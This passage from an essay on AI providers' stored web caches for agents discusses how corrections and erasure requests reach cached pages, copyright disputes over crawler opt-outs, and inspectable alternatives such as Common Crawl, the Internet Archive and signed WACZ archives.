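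That example probably exaggerates the effect, since many of the reputable sites may refuse only training crawlers. But Zhang found a similar pattern. About 26% of pages cited to support expert-checked claims refused the request, compared with 6% of pages that websites had listed specifically for AI systems. A provider could partly compensate by ranking reliable sources higher, if it has some.

Licences can fill gaps in some providers' caches. *Web Crawler Restrictions* found news outlets that refused all the popular AI crawlers but one, and that crawler's owner had a licensing agreement. Two providers' caches may therefore contain different newspapers, and a customer who switches providers may get different answers about the same event.

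### How corrections and removal requests reach a stored copy

A newspaper that corrects an article usually can't send the correction to a cache. The crawler has to revisit the page, the provider has to replace the copy and any extracts made from it, and the search system has to start using the new version. The last step can fail even after the others succeed. In tests of OpenAI's live search, Chen and colleagues found that about 60% of answers were still outdated after OpenAI had fetched the corrected page.

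A scientific journal may announce a retraction on a separate page, so a cache could hold both the notice and the original article without any sign in the article that it was retracted.

A publisher who wants a page gone quickly can block the search crawler. But a crawler that obeys the block can't detect later changes to the page, including a correction or deletion. Removing a page from search answers also may not delete the stored copy, and OpenAI doesn't say when it deletes stored copies.

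Under the European Union's General Data Protection Regulation, people named on a page can act more directly by asking an organization to erase their personal data. The organization normally has a month to respond. The right to erasure has exceptions, notably for freedom of expression. A publisher that has to erase data it made public must also take reasonable steps to inform others who hold copies.

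The EU's Court of Justice applied the earlier version of this law to search engines in its 2014 *Google Spain* ruling. It held that people can sometimes have links removed from the results of searches for their name, even if the original page is lawful and stays online. In 2022 the court added that a person who can show that the information is manifestly inaccurate doesn't have to sue the publisher first. These rulings concern search results, but the reasoning could well extend to an agent's cache, whose operator also collects pages and finds them by a person's name.

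A court order against a publisher may not name the companies that hold copies, but the person who won it can send it to an AI provider, and EU law gives the provider a reason to act. The Digital Services Act protects companies from liability for temporary caches if they meet certain conditions. They must leave the information unmodified, follow widely used rules about updating it, and quickly remove or block access to their copy once they know that the source has gone or a court has ordered its removal. US copyright law has a similar protection.

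AI providers may not qualify because their software often converts pages to another form. Chen and colleagues also found that several services largely ignored publishers' instructions about how long to reuse a page. A US court accepted Google's cache of web pages in *Field v. Google* (2006), but Google kept the copies only about two to three weeks and honoured a tag that let publishers opt out.

Copyright law on AI copying is also unsettled. Lawenda summarises the European position. EU law lets companies copy accessible works for text and data mining unless the rightholder has reserved that use, for instance by machine-readable means. Courts have disagreed about what counts as a reservation:

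- A Dutch court found a robots.txt file insufficient because it excluded only certain AI crawlers.
- A Hungarian appeal court accepted robots.txt as an objection in a case about a search engine.
- A Hamburg appeal court called it disputed whether a statement in ordinary language is enough. As of October 2026, Germany's highest civil court had not decided the appeal.

In another case, *Like Company v Google Ireland*, also pending as of October 2026, the Court of Justice was asked whether training a language model involves copying at all. None of these cases directly settles whether a provider may store a page for months and supply it to agents, so customers who depend on a cache should be aware that the provider may have to remove some of its contents.

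### Collections that outsiders can inspect

A customer who doesn't want to depend on the provider's choices has several alternatives:

| Collection | Cost | Coverage | Accountability |
|---|---|---|---|
| Provider's cache | Little extra work for the customer | Broad, but unspecified | Outsiders can test it only through its answers |
| Customer's own snapshot | Cheap storage, but staff must collect, search and update it | Only the pages the customer chose | The customer can inspect everything and show it to an auditor |
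| Common Crawl | Free to download, expensive to store and search | Billions of pages | Anyone can examine the same edition |
| Wikipedia's releases | Free, and small enough for one computer | One encyclopedia | The history of edits is public |
| Internet Archive | Free for readers, with limits on automated use | Many dated versions, with growing gaps in news | Anyone can open a dated copy |

Storing a snapshot is much easier than choosing its pages and building a good search tool. The median homepage that Chen and colleagues measured was 158 kilobytes, so a million pages of that size would take up about 158 gigabytes and fit on a laptop. AWS customers can't avoid the harder work by copying its collection, because AWS forbids them to store its search results in bulk or use them to build a competing index.

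A local snapshot doesn't make the agent's reading private if the model runs on the provider's servers, because the customer has to send the page's text there for the model to read it. Only running the model on the customer's own machines avoids this.

Common Crawl is open to everyone, but it leaves out sites that block its crawler. In a random sample of Slovak domains, Lawenda found that 2.9% of the sites Common Crawl had recorded opted out of AI training, compared with 4.8% of the sites it had missed. Common Crawl's recent crawls had recorded between 13% and 31% of each country's registered domains, though many of the rest may be inactive.

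The Internet Archive's Wayback Machine is the best of these for checking what a page contained on a certain date, because it keeps successive versions. But it isn't a safe substitute for an agent's cache, because the agent's requests would leave the provider's network, and the service can capture a missing page on demand, which would send the page's address to the website. The Archive's limits on automated access also make it unsuitable for large numbers of agents.

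Publishers are now blocking the Archive too, because they fear that AI companies will use it to get around their restrictions. The Next Web's *News publishers are blocking the Internet Archive’s Wayback Machine* dates The New York Times's "hard block" to late 2025. Fortune (2026), citing Wired, reported that 241 sites were blocking the Archive's crawler by April 2026, including those of 23 news organizations. *340 Local News Outlets Now Blocking The Internet Archive* describes the effect on a journalist in New York State who relies on archived stories from local papers that have closed.

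The fear has some basis, since a 2023 Washington Post analysis found material from the Internet Archive in major AI training datasets. But according to Techdirt's *News Publishers Are Now Blocking The Internet Archive*, The Guardian restricted access without documenting any AI company taking its articles through the Archive. The Archive says it limits, filters and monitors automated access. The blocks also remove independent copies that outsiders could have used to check what an AI provider's cache contains.

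Archive formats could make such checks more reliable. The standard one, WARC, stores a server's response together with its address and capture time. A newer format, WACZ, packages these records and has a method for signing them:

1. The archivist's software computes a hash of each file.
2. It lists the hashes and signs the list.
3. A separate timestamp service certifies when the signature existed.

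Once an archivist signs a package of stored pages, anyone can verify that nobody has altered it since. The signature doesn't prove that the website sent those pages, because a dishonest archivist could sign a forgery. Agreement between two independent archives is better evidence. Publishers could also sign their own pages, but few would do so just to help auditors.

A provider could use the same method by returning a signed hash and capture date with every page an agent reads. An outsider who later obtained the page could confirm that the provider had served that version. OpenAI describes nothing like this for offline search.

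### The case for one keeper

Central control has advantages for security. A provider can scan the whole collection and withdraw a malicious page for every customer at once. If 5,000 companies kept their own snapshots, each would have to learn about the page and delete it, and some would not. Erasure requests would be harder still to handle, because the person named on the page wouldn't know which companies had copies.

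A single operator can also enforce a policy more consistently. When an organization requires Codex's indexed mode, for example, OpenAI's server applies the same check to every developer's requests. Few companies could afford a security team to maintain an equally large cache of their own.

For most organizations, the provider's cache is the sensible default for general research. A small snapshot of their own is worth the effort for documents they must be able to produce later, such as the regulations or medical guidance behind a decision. In their own snapshot, they can record capture dates and keep old versions, which the provider doesn't promise to do.

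If a single provider keeps the cache and wrongly withdraws a page, every customer loses it, and few will notice. Search engines faced a similar problem with removal requests, and Google sends copies of many of those it receives to Lumen, a public database that researchers can search. AI providers could do the same when they remove a page from a cache, leaving out the details of people who asked for erasure.
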